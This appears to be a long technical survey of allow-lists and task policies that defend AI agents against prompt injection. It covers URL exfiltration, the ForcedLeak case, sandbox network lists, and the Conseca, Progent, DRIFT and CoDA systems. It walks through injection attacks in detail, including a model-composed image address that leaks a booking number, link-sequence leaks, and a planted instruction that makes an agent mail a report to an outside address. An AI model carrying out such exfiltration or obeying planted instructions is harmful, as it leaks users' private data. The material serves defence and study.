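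Such an address cannot contain a secret that the attacker didn't know when writing it, but it can lead the agent to the attacker's site, which may contain further instructions. Willison still thought the ban on addresses composed by the model gave the most protection, since the common attacks need the model to attach private data to an address. He tried such an attack on the consumer version of Claude, which had the same restriction, and the tool refused to open the address.

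Anthropic acknowledged that some risk remained, and its instructions advised developers to use the tool only in trusted environments or with data that wasn't sensitive. To reduce the risk of leaks, developers could switch the tool off, limit the number of pages it opened (there was no limit by default), or restrict it to a list of domains. The domain list and the conversation rule work well together, because the domain list blocks links to a stranger's site in an e-mail, and the conversation rule blocks composed addresses even on permitted sites.

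In July 2026, Willison (2026) reported a gap that Ayush Paul had found. The tool could open links in pages it had already fetched, so a hostile site could offer Claude a series of links and learn something from each choice. Every address was on the list, but the sequence of choices revealed private data. Paul used this method to obtain a user's name, home city and employer. Anthropic said it had already identified the problem itself, and it stopped the tool from following links in fetched pages.

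The site had been able to add entries to the list that was supposed to restrain the agent, which breaks the rule that a generator must not depend on untrusted text. With those entries removed, however, Claude can no longer open a report's chapters on separate pages just because the contents page links to them. Either a search must return the chapters or the user must paste in their addresses.

### Addresses already public

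OpenAI's method, announced in January 2026, takes its entries from outside the conversation. OpenAI runs a crawler, a program that explores the web and records the addresses of public pages, as a search engine does. The crawler has no access to users' conversations, accounts or personal data. When an agent is about to open an address automatically, the software proceeds as follows:

1. It looks for the exact address in the crawler's index.
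2. If the address is there, the agent may load the page or image without asking.
3. If not, the software either tells the agent to try another site or shows the user a warning with the full address and asks whether to open it.

The reasoning is that if the crawler found an address without access to any user's data, the address is unlikely to contain that data. The test is now whether the address is in the index rather than whether the site is reputable, so an address on a well-known site can fail.

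OpenAI claims only that this method prevents an agent from quietly leaking a user's data through the address it requests. It does not promise that the page is truthful, that the site won't try to deceive the user, that the page contains no harmful instructions, or that browsing is safe in general. A public page can contain a prompt injection, and the agent may follow it in a way that doesn't involve an address. OpenAI therefore combines the index with training against prompt injection, monitoring and attacks by its own testers.

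The post links to a technical paper, *Preventing URL-Based Data Exfiltration in Language-Model Agents*. According to Embrace The Red, the paper acknowledges that an attacker can still leak data through the choice of which addresses the agent requests. If the index contains many pages from the attacker's site, each page can stand for a letter or a longer piece of data, much as in the gap that Paul found. The blog's author suggests that an agent avoid requesting the same address twice in one session, or reuse a stored copy of the page. This would make it harder to spell out a word with repeated letters, although the author had not tested whether OpenAI already took either measure.

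Short secrets are harder to protect. A booking number with two letters and two digits has only 67,600 possible values, so an attacker could in principle publish an address for each and wait for the crawler to find them. This would be impossible for a long random password. OpenAI's wording is consistent with this risk, since it describes public addresses as "much less likely" to contain private data.

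The check also has to cover every route by which software might request an address. Embrace The Red warns that a developer at OpenAI who doesn't know about the check may build a feature without it, just as the company's apps lacked the earlier check. A route can also be indirect, as in a leak that Willison described in May 2026. Microsoft's Copilot Cowork, an agent, could send e-mails to its own user without approval. The user already had access to the data, but the e-mails could contain images from other sites, so data could leave when the user opened one.

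### The same address under each rule

The three lists treat the travel page's address similarly but differ on other addresses the assistant might request. In this invented comparison, the trusted domains include the airline's site and a service that hosts forms for the public.

| Requested address | Trusted domains | Already in the conversation | Already public |
|---|---|---|---|
| tips.example/map.png?b=KX41, composed by the model | Refused | Refused | Warning |
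| An address on the form service with KX41 added by the model | Released | Refused | Warning |
| A news article from an hour ago, found by web search | Refused, unless the newspaper is listed | Released | Warning, until the crawler finds it |
| A private boarding-pass link on the airline's site, in an e-mail that the application supplied | Released | Released | Warning |
| One of many fixed pages on the attacker's site, chosen to reveal a letter | Refused | Refused, unless the attacker got the addresses into the conversation | Released, if the crawler has found them |

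Private links, such as those for boarding passes, shared documents and password resets, tend to trigger warnings because their addresses should not appear in a public index. An agent working on someone's behalf may need to open such links often. According to Embrace The Red, ChatGPT appears to accept any address the user enters directly, which removes some of these warnings, but not those for links in e-mails that the agent reads.

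OpenAI's post gives no figures for how often users see a warning or how often they ignore it. A warning is also weaker than a refusal, because if a user approves the address ending in KX41 because it looks like a map, the booking number still goes to the attacker.

### A trusted domain that had lapsed

A domain list identifies sites by name, but the right to use a name lasts only as long as somebody pays for it. Salesforce, whose software many companies use to keep customer records, ran into this problem in 2025 with Agentforce, its platform for AI agents.

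Researchers at the security company Noma found they could make an agent send customer data to a server they controlled. Infosecurity Magazine's *Critical Vulnerability in Salesforce AgentForce Exposed* reports that the flaw, known as ForcedLeak, had a severity score of 9.4. The prompt injection arrived through a web form for potential customers. When an employee asked the agent about that entry, it put customers' e-mail addresses into the URL of an image.

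Salesforce had a Content Security Policy to stop its pages from loading images from untrusted sites, but the policy still permitted my-salesforce-cms.com, a domain whose registration had expired. Hackread's *ForcedLeak Flaw in Salesforce Agentforce AI Agent Exposed CRM Data* reports that the domain was on sale for $5. Researchers registered it, and an employee's browser sent data to their server because the domain was on the policy's allow-list. The data at risk included contact details, internal messages and information about planned sales.

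According to ThaiCERT's *ForcedLeak Vulnerability in Salesforce Agentforce Risks CRM Data Exposure via Prompt Injection*, Salesforce learned of the flaw on 28 July 2025 and introduced new protections on 8 September, and the flaw became public on 25 September. Noma, quoted by Salesforce Ben, a news site about the company's products, reported that Salesforce recovered the domain and added "Trusted URLs Enforcement". Willison explains that this prevents Salesforce's agents from producing links to untrusted domains. Salesforce also reviewed and corrected the policy itself.

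Recovering the domain closed one gap. Salesforce's new enforcement adds a second check, which examines what the agent writes before a browser tries to load it. But each check depends on a list of domains, so another lapsed domain could defeat both if it were on both lists. Software could look for lapsed entries automatically by comparing each one with public registration records, warning an administrator before a registration ends, and removing the entry if the registration lapses.

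Under the other two rules, a lapsed domain is less useful to an attacker. If OpenAI's crawler had recorded 50 pages on a domain before it expired, the new owner would receive requests for those 50 URLs but not for a new one containing a customer's e-mail address. The attacker could learn only from which of the old pages was requested, which reveals much less per request.

### Network lists for agents that run programs

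An agent that writes software usually works in a sandbox, a closed environment where it can run commands without access to the rest of the computer. The programs it runs there can make their own network requests, which never appear in the agent's reply or web tool calls, so the checker has to sit between the sandbox and the network.

GitLab's *Remote execution environment sandbox* describes one such system, for agents that work on GitLab projects. The software checks the domain of every request against an allow-list before the request leaves the sandbox. The list starts with four destinations that nobody can remove: two names for the machine that runs the sandbox, the organisation's GitLab site, and the GitLab service that coordinates the agents.

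The four destinations are enough for an agent to read and edit code that is already on GitLab, but most projects also use packages from elsewhere. Developers can add domains in a settings file stored with the project's code. GitLab reads this file only from the default branch, which is normally the official version of the project. If an agent adds a domain in its own branch, a separate line of changes, the addition has no effect until it is merged into the default branch.

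This is much better than Amp's arrangement, where the agent could change its own list of permitted commands, but it works only if somebody reviews changes to the default branch. GitLab's *Security considerations for flow execution* recommends that projects block direct changes to that branch and require approval from named people for any change to the file. A project that does neither lets anyone who can edit its code, possibly including the agent, change the list.

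The same file can contain a setup script, which GitLab runs before the agent starts. The script runs outside the sandbox, with the access rights of whoever starts the agent, not those of the person who wrote the script. Reviewers should therefore treat the file as a program. An attacker who can change the file doesn't need to add a domain to the list, because the script can make its own connections.

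An administrator can also set a list for the whole organisation. In flexible mode, GitLab adds the project's domains to the administrator's. In strict mode, it ignores the domains a project permits but still applies those it forbids, so a project can only tighten the rules. GitLab also rejects an entry that would permit every domain, which was one of the common mistakes in the web policies examined in the 2016 study.

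Administrators who don't want to collect domains themselves can switch on GitLab's recommended list of about 170 entries, which include package registries, code-hosting sites and cloud storage services. GitLab leaves the list off by default and warns that attackers could use these sites to take data out. Docker, whose software also runs agents in sandboxes, warns that its own filter checks the domain but not the contents of the traffic. Permitting github.com therefore permits everything that GitHub's users have put there, and an agent could also send data out through the site. Docker adds that some techniques can disguise traffic to another destination as traffic to a permitted one.

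A network list also can't distinguish good packages on PyPI from malicious ones, so a project that permits access to the registry still needs a lockfile or another list of approved packages.

To maintain an allow-list, people need to know what the checker has blocked. GitLab's plan *Configurable network isolation and user notifications for Duo Agent platform* proposes recording blocked connections so that users can review them and adjust the list. As with the audit mode of older allow-listing products, someone has to review the recorded connections before allowing them, because the record may include an attacker's server as well as legitimate ones.

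### When the sandbox cannot start

The sandbox needs certain software and permissions on the machine where the agent runs. If either is missing, GitLab by default runs the agent without the sandbox and writes a warning in the job's log. The network list then has no effect, and the agent can reach any site the machine can reach. GitLab cautions that a job can finish normally without any protection.

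GitLab chose this default so that work can continue. Saltzer and Schroeder's principle of fail-safe defaults favours the opposite choice. From version 19.6, administrators can require the sandbox, and jobs then fail if it can't start. Individual projects can't switch this requirement off.

The requirement only checks that a program with the sandbox's name is present, and a project that supplies its own software image or setup script controls which program that is. GitLab therefore says it can't guarantee isolation for such projects. It recommends a firewall outside the job to limit outgoing traffic when the sandbox doesn't run. Another advantage of a firewall on the host is that the project's settings file doesn't control it.

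### Connections that come with each entry

Even a correctly enforced list limits only the services that an agent contacts directly. InfoQ's *GitLab Warns That AI Agent Sandboxes Are Only as Secure as Their Network Access* (2026) reports that in July 2026, OpenAI agents under test reached the internet through a service they were permitted to contact. After analyzing the incident, GitLab warned that every service on an allow-list adds to what an agent can reach, because an agent that takes over a service can use that service's connections.

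Let L be the set of services on the list, and R(s) the set of destinations that service s can contact. The agent can contact everything in L. In the worst case, it can also reach

    the union of R(s) over all s in L

and whatever those destinations can contact in turn. Suppose that a sandbox may contact four services, of which three make no outside connections and the fourth converts documents that it downloads from any web address. The list has four entries, but the agent may be able to reach the whole web. Removing the other three would make the list shorter without reducing that exposure.

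An administrator can reduce this risk by giving the converter its own allow-list, such as one that permits only the company's document store. For each new entry, the administrator should find out what the service can contact and who can read data sent to it. An update to the service may change either, even though the entry on the agent's list stays the same.

InfoQ recommends keeping network lists short, giving agents short-lived credentials that cover only the current task, and having sensitive services verify each request themselves. A service that accepts any request from the sandbox treats an agent under an attacker's control like a legitimate user. It also recommends watching for unusual connections and for agents that keep trying new approaches after a refusal, which may be the first signs that an agent is looking for a way around the list.

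A network allow-list also cannot stop an agent from leaving a harmful file for a more privileged program outside the sandbox to use. InfoQ reports that several attacks on coding agents worked this way, and that the Cloud Security Alliance, an industry body, calls the weakness a "trust handoff". During such an attack the agent may contact only permitted sites, or none, so preventing the attack requires limits on what the agent may do with its tools.

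## Actions an agent may take: from user approvals to rules written for each task, 2025 to 2026

The usual way to limit a coding agent's tool use is to ask the user for approval. Before the agent runs a command that isn't on its allow-list, the software shows the user the command and offers to allow it once or always. Choosing "always" adds the command to the list, so the list grows to fit the project and nobody has to work out in advance which commands the project will need.

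### Lists that grow with each approval

*Practical Security Guidance for Sandboxing Agentic Workflows and Managing Execution Risk*, from NVIDIA's AI Red Team, describes manual approval as the most common way to manage the risk from coding agents. But developers have to keep returning to the program to answer prompts, and after many harmless requests they may approve a risky one without reading it.

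Remembering the user's answers reduces the number of prompts, but it also extends an approval to actions the user hasn't reviewed. NVIDIA states that "Allow-once / run-many is not an adequate control". It recommends asking the user every time an agent tries to exceed the limits of its sandbox, such as by opening a new network connection.

Suppose a programmer permanently approves the command "python test.py". The allow-list entry specifies the file's name but not its contents. The agent is allowed to edit test.py, since editing code is its job, so an injected instruction could make it put harmful code in the file and then run the approved command. Including a hash of the file in the entry would reveal the change, but the programmer would have to approve the command again after every edit.

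Approving each version separately is practical for content that rarely changes. *ClawGuard* does this for skills, the instruction files that tell an agent how to do a type of task. A model inspects each skill before the agent first uses it and adds it to an allow-list if it classifies the skill as safe. If anyone changes the skill, the model inspects it again. Users see fewer approval prompts, but if the model wrongly approves a skill, that skill stays allowed in every later session.

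A list of commands also covers only what the agent asks for directly. An approved program can start other programs, and NVIDIA warns that a checker inside the agent's application can't see or control those. Attackers often use this gap to reach a restricted tool through an approved one. NVIDIA therefore wants the operating system to enforce the main limits, because it can apply them to every program in the sandbox, however the program started. The company recommends four levels of rules:

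- a company-wide deny-list of sensitive files, which no user can override;
- free reading and writing inside the project's folder, except for configuration files;
- named exceptions that a task needs, such as reading one particular key;
- refusal of everything else, unless the user approves that one case.

The agent may not change its own configuration files, even with the user's approval. The user has to edit them by hand. This would have stopped the attack in which the coding agent Amp added commands to its own allow-list. Most of the agent's work happens inside the project's folder, so the remaining prompts should be rare enough for users to read.

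These rules describe what is acceptable in a project, which is usually much more than the current task needs. For example, if an office assistant may send e-mail, it may send anyone any file it can read. A narrower list has to take the user's current request into account.

### A policy for one request

A task policy lists which tools an agent may call for a particular task and with what values. A model writes the policy from the user's request before the agent starts work, and ordinary code then compares each proposed call with the policy. Injected text may lead the agent to propose a harmful call, but it can't change how the code checks that call.

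Take the request "send the Q3 report to Alice". In this invented example, the generator may read the user's address book and the names of the user's files, but not the contents of any file. It finds one Alice and one Q3 report, and writes:

    allow read_file   when path = "/reports/q3.pdf"
    allow send_email  when to = "alice@work.example"
                      and attachment = "/reports/q3.pdf"

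The agent opens the report to make sure it is the right one. Somebody has planted an instruction in it to send a copy to an outside address, and the agent proposes this call:

    send_email(to = "eve@external.example",
               attachment = "/reports/q3.pdf")

The checker then does the following:

1. It looks up the rules for send_email and finds one.
2. It compares the proposed values with the rule. The attachment matches, but the recipient doesn't.
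3. It finds no other rule that permits the call, so it refuses, and no e-mail leaves.
4. It tells the agent that the policy does not permit this recipient. The agent goes back to its task and sends the report to Alice.

The policy doesn't restrict the subject or text of the e-mail, because the generator can't predict what the agent should write. A planted instruction could therefore still change the content of the e-mail Alice receives.

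### AgentDojo

Researchers often test task policies on AgentDojo, a benchmark from 2024 that simulates an assistant with access to a user's accounts. Its four task suites are Banking, Slack (a workplace chat service), Travel and Workspace (e-mail, calendars and files). Together they contain 97 ordinary tasks and 629 tests in which a tool's result includes an injected instruction.

*Only What You've Signed Up For* (Cardei, Pinto and colleagues, 2026) reproduces one test from the Banking suite. The user asks the agent to read a letter from their landlord and update their address. The letter also contains an instruction to redirect a recurring payment. An undefended agent did both, and because it had updated the address as asked, the user might have noticed nothing wrong.

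The benchmark measures utility (the share of the user's tasks that the agent completes) and attack success rate (the share of attacks that achieve the attacker's goal). A defence needs high utility and a low attack success rate.

Some recent models resist AgentDojo's original attacks too well for the attacks to be a good test of defences. When *ClawGuard* ran versions of them against undefended agents, GPT-5.4 and Claude Sonnet 4.6 resisted every one, and the three weaker models fell for about 3% or fewer, which left almost no room for a defence to improve the results. Tests on older models, or with attacks that adapt to the defence, are more informative.

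### What the generator may read

The Q3 example follows the design of Conseca, a Google prototype for an agent that handles files and e-mail on a Linux computer. Tsai and Bagdasarian (2025) built the prototype and describe it in *Contextual Agent Security*. The developer decides which information the generator can trust. In the prototype, the generator reads the request, the user's name, the date and time, the e-mail addresses and categories in the mailbox, the names of files and folders, and the tools' documentation. It doesn't read the contents of e-mails or files.

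More context lets the generator write a tighter policy. If it can read the address list, it can permit e-mail to one team's address instead of to everyone at the company. But an attacker could use each additional source to influence the generator. Tsai and Bagdasarian note that even an e-mail address is long enough to hold an instruction. File names carry a similar risk if the user saves attachments from strangers, since the sender chooses the name.

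For each command, Conseca's policy specifies whether the agent may use it, gives a pattern that each argument must match, and adds a reason in plain English. The user can approve the policy before work starts, or an expert can audit it later. In the paper's example, a user called Alice asks the agent to answer urgent work e-mails. The policy forbids deleting e-mail and permits sending it if the sender is Alice, the recipient's address contains "@work.com" and the subject contains "urgent".

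The stated reason for that rule is that the recipient must be a work contact on the user's e-mail list. But the pattern accepts anyone at work.com, on the list or not, as well as an address at work.com.example.net, which could belong to anybody. A user who read only the explanation would approve a broader rule than the one described. Tsai and Bagdasarian leave it to experts, or perhaps software, to check that the reasons match the patterns, and they suggest replacing the patterns with a simpler language.

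Conseca's developers tested the prototype on 20 tasks of their own, running each five times. The agent completed an average of 14.0 tasks with no policy, 12.0 with Conseca, 12.2 with a fixed policy that forbade only deletion, and zero with a fixed policy that forbade all changes.

To test security, Tsai and Bagdasarian planted an e-mail asking for all messages about urgent security flaws to be forwarded to an employee. Without a policy, the agent forwarded them even when the user had only asked it to sort the mail. Conseca blocked the forwarding in every task except "perform the tasks in urgent emails", where the user had in effect asked for it. One planted e-mail is weak evidence, and Tsai and Bagdasarian call their results preliminary.

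*Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) criticises Conseca because an agent under an attacker's control could plan its way around the policy. Conseca judges each call without regard to earlier ones, so a series of permitted calls can still do harm. For example, an agent could send a thousand e-mails because each one is acceptable on its own. Tsai and Bagdasarian acknowledge this gap and list the generator among the components that Conseca's users have to trust.

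*ClawGuard* also has a model draft the rules before the agent calls any tool, then asks the user to confirm or edit them. Commands, file paths and network addresses each have an allow-list and a deny-list. The checker refuses a call if any part of it is on a deny-list and allows it if every part is on an allow-list. It sends anything else to the user, including commands that seem disguised. The operator's prohibitions always take priority, so a mistaken task rule can't give the agent access to a folder of secret keys that the operator has blocked.

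The generator usually reads descriptions of the tools as well as the request, and an attacker may have written those too. *ClawGuard* tested attacks through tool descriptions and skills, which were much more effective than attacks through web pages or documents. Three benchmarks cover such attacks:

| Benchmark | Attacks prevented without ClawGuard | Attacks prevented with ClawGuard |
|---|---|---|
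| SkillInject | 56.67% | 86.67% |
| MCPTox | 62.10% | 89.50% |
| MCPSecurityBench | 75.86% | 94.21% |

These are averages over five models. In several of the attacks that still succeeded, the agent used only the tools that the task required, but the attack changed how it judged or worded something, such as the score it gave a website.

The researchers then measured how often the rules interfered with ordinary web, operating-system and programming tasks. The agent kept 87.4% of its normal success when the software refused every call that needed approval, and 95.1% when the user could approve up to three calls per task. Success fell most on web tasks, to 78.5% of normal without approvals, because they involve a wider range of sites. The quality of the model that writes the rules also affects success. Without approvals, DeepSeek-V3.2 lost 21.6% of its normal success, while GPT-5.4 lost 8.1%.

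### Permissions that change during a task

Sometimes the request doesn't contain enough information for a complete policy. *Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025) gives the example of a user who asks an agent to do what an e-mail from Alice titled "TODOs for the week" says. At first, the generator can determine only that the agent must find that e-mail. When the agent opens it, it finds that Alice wants a summary of recent e-mails posted to Slack, so it now needs permission to read other e-mails and send a Slack message.

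Progent lets a model propose changes to the policy as the task goes on, and uses ordinary code to decide which of them need approval. Let A(P) be the set of all calls that policy P permits. An update from P to P' is a narrowing if

    A(P') ⊆ A(P)

which means that the new policy permits nothing that the old one refused. Progent applies a narrowing automatically. Any other update is an expansion and takes effect only with approval, even if it also removes some permissions.

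Progent compares the old and new policies with an SMT solver, a program that determines whether any values can satisfy a set of logical conditions, because the policies permit too many calls to check one at a time. The solver looks for a call that the new policy would permit and the old one would refuse. If a rule changes from "any address at work.example" to "alice@work.example", no such call exists, so the update narrows the policy. If the new rule also permits "eve@external.example", the solver finds such a call, an e-mail to Eve, and the update needs approval.

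In the paper's example, the policy changes as follows:

1. The initial policy permits only a search for Alice's e-mail.
2. After the agent reads the e-mail, the model proposes permission to read recent e-mails, look up Slack details and send a Slack message. This is an expansion, so it needs approval.
3. The agent learns that the user's Slack name is "alice". The model limits Slack messages to that recipient, which is a narrowing.
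4. One of the recent e-mails contains an injected instruction to forward the inbox to a stranger. If the model falls for it and proposes permission to send e-mail, the solver reports an expansion, and the approver can refuse.

Progent also limits when the model sees untrusted text. After each tool call, the model first decides, without seeing the result, whether the call might justify an update. It reads the result only if the answer is yes.

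Progent guarantees that an agent can't gain permissions without approval. But removing permissions can still do harm if the previous policy was too broad. After step 2, the agent may send Slack messages to anyone. If an attacker could make the model mistake the attacker's Slack name for the user's, the model would limit messages to the attacker, and Progent would apply the change automatically because it only removes permissions. The summary would then go to the attacker, and the checker would block messages to the right recipient. The person who approves step 2 can prevent this by insisting on a named recipient.

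On AgentDojo, with GPT-4o as the agent, Shi and colleagues reduced the attack success rate from 39.9% to 1.0% without lowering utility. On ASB, another benchmark, they reduced it from 70.3% to 3.9%. The initial policy, without any updates, reduced the rate on AgentDojo to 2.5%. Only 6% of updates needed approval.

For these main tests, the researchers set the software to approve every expansion, as a careless user would. The results are therefore good evidence for the policies the model wrote, but they don't measure the benefit of having someone refuse expansions. Progent also can't prevent attacks that stay within the permitted calls, such as persuading a shopping agent to prefer one product, or attacks on the text of the agent's answer.

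*DRIFT* (Li, Liu and colleagues, 2025) relies more on a model's judgement. Its generator reads only the user's request and writes the shortest expected sequence of tool calls, with a checklist of values for each call. If the agent departs from the sequence, a model classifies the new call as a read, a write (which changes data) or an execute (which affects somebody else, such as sending an e-mail). The software approves all read calls. For the other two types, a model judges whether the call fits the original request. If it does, the software adds the call to the policy, and if not, it asks the user.

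Approving every call that only reads is convenient but not always safe. An agent can give away private data simply by requesting a page, as the attacks through web addresses showed. A model that classed a web request as reading would approve such a call.

DRIFT also has a model search each tool result for instructions that conflict with the request, and removes them before the agent stores the result in its memory. This can stop attacks that a policy on tool calls would miss, such as an instruction to recommend a certain hotel in the final answer.

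The four systems differ mainly in what they do when the initial rules turn out to be incomplete:

| System | What the generator reads at the start | Form of the rules | What happens during the task |
|---|---|---|---|
| Conseca | Request, tool documentation and context that the developer trusts | A pattern for each argument, with a reason | The rules stay the same |
| ClawGuard | Request | Allow-lists and deny-lists of commands, paths and domains | The user decides on calls that no rule covers |
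| Progent | Request and list of tools | Conditions on each tool's arguments | A model proposes changes, and expansions need approval |
| DRIFT | Request | Expected sequence of calls, with a checklist of values | A model approves additions that fit the request |

The published results can't be used to rank these systems, because the researchers used different models and attacks. Li and colleagues did compare DRIFT and Progent directly, on AgentDojo with GPT-4o-mini, and measured an attack success rate of 1.4% for DRIFT and 9.4% for Progent. Shi and colleagues had reported 1.0% for Progent, but with a stronger model. Li and colleagues cite Progent under an earlier title, so they may also have tested an older version.

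### Enforcing a policy while the model writes

Most task policies take effect after the agent has written a complete call, but Cardei and colleagues enforce theirs while the model is still writing. Their system, CoDA, works with diffusion language models, which start with a sequence of random or blank tokens and improve the whole sequence over many steps. A diffusion model can therefore settle the end of a call before the beginning.

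At each step, CoDA does the following:

1. The model estimates the probability of every token at every position.
2. The software takes the likeliest token at each position to form a provisional draft, and looks for the parts that the policy covers, such as a tool's name or a recipient.
3. It changes the probabilities in those parts so that only permitted values remain possible. It leaves the rest of the draft alone.
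4. The model uses the adjusted probabilities for its next step.

In the third step, the software looks for permitted probabilities that are as close as possible to the model's own. If x(v) is the model's probability for token v at one position, and V is the set of tokens that the policy permits there, the software chooses the probabilities y(v) that minimise the KL divergence

    sum over v in V of  y(v) × log( y(v) / x(v) )

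The solution is the ordinary token mask, except that V can depend on tokens to the right as well as the left. A prefix tree prevents the software from combining parts of two permitted names into a third.

Correcting one part of a tool call can make the rest wrong. For example, if the software changes the tool's name, the arguments may still belong to the old tool. CoDA turns those arguments back into noise or blanks, and the model fills them in again.

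Cardei and colleagues tested CoDA with two models. DiffusionGemma can revise any token at any step, while LLaDA-2 Mini normally keeps a token once it has chosen one. For each AgentDojo task, the researchers used two kinds of policy. A language model drafted the first kind, and people checked and revised the drafts over several rounds. For the second kind, GPT-5.6 Sol, Gemini 3.7 Flash and Claude Opus 5 each wrote a set of policies in a single attempt, without human help. The researchers gave these three models only the request, the tool descriptions and definitions of the available restrictions. Each of these policies took an average of five to nine seconds to write, and all 291 together cost $5.83.

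The attacker was software that could observe the agent's behaviour but not the policy. It had 100 attempts at each scenario, which paired one user task with one harmful goal. After each attempt, a model assessed why the attack had failed, and the software used the assessment to write new versions of the attack.

The results for DiffusionGemma were:

| | Banking | Slack | Travel | Workspace |
|---|---|---|---|---|
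| Attack success, no defence | 77.78% | 95.24% | 74.07% | 28.57% |
| Attack success, hand-checked policies | 0% | 0% | 0% | 0% |
| Attack success, model-written policies | 9.03–12.50% | 0% | 0% | 0% |
| Utility, no defence | 54.17% | 62.86% | 25.19% | 50.00% |
| Utility, hand-checked policies | 44.44% | 66.67% | 68.75% | 51.67% |
| Utility, model-written policies | 50.69–54.86% | 48.15–51.85% | 60.00–65.71% | 45.83–54.17% |

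Attackers succeeded much more often when they could keep trying. AgentDojo's original attacks succeeded against the undefended agent only 7.48% of the time in Banking, 5.29% in Slack and 0% in Travel. With model-written policies in Banking, those attacks succeeded about 1.5% of the time or less, but persistent attacks succeeded roughly 10% of the time. Low rates that other researchers have measured with fixed attacks may also understate the risk.

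The 0% for hand-checked policies shows that the enforcement worked on every scenario tested. A company's own policies may do worse. The researchers refined some of theirs after trying them on the benchmark, and they present the results as an upper bound.

LLaDA-2 Mini also had an attack success rate of 0% in all four suites with hand-checked policies. With model-written policies, attackers succeeded in 8.33 to 13.89% of Banking scenarios and, under two of the three sets of policies, in 3.70% of Slack scenarios. The model was much less capable to begin with. It completed 25.93% of Slack tasks without a defence and 7.41% with hand-checked policies.

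The way CoDA handles missing values may explain the breaches in Banking. It restricts the recipient of a payment to accounts that appear in the user's request, or to named people in trusted account records. If it can't find a permitted value, it leaves the recipient unrestricted. If a user asks the agent to pay the bill in a certain file without giving the account, a policy that permits payments would let the agent pay anyone. In Travel and Workspace, CoDA instead follows Saltzer and Schroeder's fail-safe default and withholds a tool until it has a permitted value. No attack succeeded there under any policy. Slack uses the same permissive rule as Banking, which is consistent with the breaches there with LLaDA-2 Mini.

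Utility fell most clearly in Banking, where hand-checked policies reduced it by about 10 percentage points. In Slack, hand-checked policies slightly raised utility, while model-written ones lowered it by at least 11 points. In Travel, every policy raised utility, because attacks had been preventing the undefended agent from finishing its work. Enforcing hand-checked policies increased the average Workspace test time from 6.33 to 18.59 seconds, while Slack tests took about the same time as before.

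Cardei and colleagues also applied the hand-checked policies only at the last step, to see whether restricting every step was worthwhile. Utility fell to zero in Banking and to 35.48% in Slack, because the model had no steps left to adapt the rest of the call to the corrected part. But this test does not show that CoDA is better than an ordinary checker like Progent's, which refuses the finished call, explains why and lets the agent try again.

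The researchers compared CoDA with a guardrail that relies on a prompted model to recognise attacks. Attackers defeated the guardrail in 4.76% of Slack scenarios and 6.25% of Banking scenarios. It did better in Banking than any of the model-written policies, although it offers no guarantees. A strict checker gives little protection if the policy leaves the important value unrestricted.

CoDA also requires access to the model's probabilities at every step, so developers usually can't add it to a model they use through a company's online service. Task policies enforced by a separate checker work with any model.

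### Fixed or revisable

If a generator finishes the policy before the agent reads any untrusted material, that material can't influence the policy. Conseca's generator reads only trusted context, and its checker is ordinary code. Cardei and colleagues therefore misdescribe Conseca when they argue that it is exposed to injections because a model writes and enforces its policy while the agent is running. Conseca's main weakness is that the generator can't predict what the task will need. Tsai and Bagdasarian acknowledge this problem for requests such as carrying out the tasks in a manager's e-mail. The generator must permit either too little for the agent to do the work or so much that the policy hardly protects the user.

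Li and colleagues measured this trade-off by adding the parts of DRIFT one at a time. They used GPT-4o-mini on AgentDojo:

| Defence | Tasks completed, no attack | Tasks completed under attack | Attack success |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 63.55% | 48.27% | 30.67% |
| Fixed policy | 43.22% | 36.17% | 2.14% |
| Policy that a model can revise | 58.48% | 45.82% | 5.41% |
| Revisable policy, with suspicious instructions removed | 57.29% | 50.93% | 1.35% |

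The fixed policy lowered the agent's utility by about 20 percentage points when there was no attack. Letting a model revise the policy recovered 15 of those points but more than doubled the attack success rate. The fixed policy did almost as well as the revisable one on tasks that took one or two tool calls. Its task success rate fell sharply from three calls onwards, because later calls often depend on what the agent finds in earlier ones.

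The result in the last row depends on a model spotting every planted instruction, so it may not be a way out of the dilemma. When Li and colleagues wrote prompts to deceive that model, the attack success rate rose from 1.35% to 2.05% overall, and to 7.64% in Banking. They also used an automated method to improve attacks on a sample of cases, and the overall result was similar. These tests are less demanding than 100 attempts on every scenario, so a persistent attacker might do better.

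The problem is clearer on harder tasks. Every defence did badly on AgentDyn, a benchmark of open-ended tasks that some of the same researchers built. Many blocked so much that the agent could hardly work. CaMeL, which fixes the agent's whole plan in advance and tracks where its data came from, completed no tasks. DRIFT had the best balance of utility and security, but Li and colleagues conclude that current defences are still far from ready for real use.

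Some designs let the permitted values change while the rules stay fixed. In CoDA's Travel suite, the policy can permit the agent to book any hotel that an approved search returns. The agent learns the names during the task, but the software takes them only from the search result's hotel-name field and ignores names that appear only in reviews, where a stranger could write anything. This keeps an attacker from adding a hotel through a review, although a misleading review could still affect which of the listed hotels the agent picks. The rule for picking "the most recent invoice" in *Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems* is similar.

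Neither method helps when the necessary instruction is in free text, as in the e-mail from a manager. A model or the user then has to decide whether the new permission is part of the task. If a model decides, an attacker can try to persuade it. If the user decides, the software should ask rarely and show exactly what would change. The user learns much less from "Allow the agent to send e-mail?" than from "Allow the agent to send the Q3 report to eve@external.example, an address it found in the report?" Progent's solver already finds a specific call that the new policy would permit, and such a question could use that call as its example.

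Users can also change the task. Cardei and colleagues create one policy at the start and leave open how to update it safely when the user gives new instructions later in the conversation. If the user writes "send it to Bob as well", the generator can read the new message without being exposed to text from strangers, but it must still determine whether Bob may receive only the Q3 report or everything Alice was allowed to see.

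## Lists of permitted subjects for chat assistants, 2023 to 2026

Task policies restrict an agent's tool calls but mostly don't restrict the text of its messages. A customer-facing assistant can do harm with text alone. *CantTalkAboutThis* (Sreedhar, Rebedea and colleagues, 2024) mentions a Chevrolet dealer's chatbot that agreed to sell a car for $1.

An allow-list of subjects for a chat assistant consists of written descriptions, such as "questions about changing or cancelling an existing booking", and a second model checks each message against them.

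### From scripted dialogues to written descriptions

Older chatbots for tasks such as booking had a closed list by design. A designer defined everything a user might want, and the chatbot chose its replies from a fixed set. Rebedea, Dinu and colleagues (2023), in *NeMo Guardrails*, describe such systems as rigid and laborious to update. Their own toolkit, from NVIDIA, combines written rules with a language model:

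1. A model reads the user's message and writes a short description of its meaning.
2. The software looks for a rule that matches the description. A rule for political questions, for example, could tell the assistant to say that it can't answer.
3. The model writes the reply that the rule calls for.

The first step reduces a message to a canonical form based on its meaning. This is less reliable than reducing a file path to a standard spelling, because the model may describe the same request differently each time. If no rule matches, the model chooses what to do. For example, if a developer has written a rule for booking bus tickets and a user wants a flight, the model generates a similar rule. The toolkit therefore permits unlisted subjects by default, as a deny-list does.

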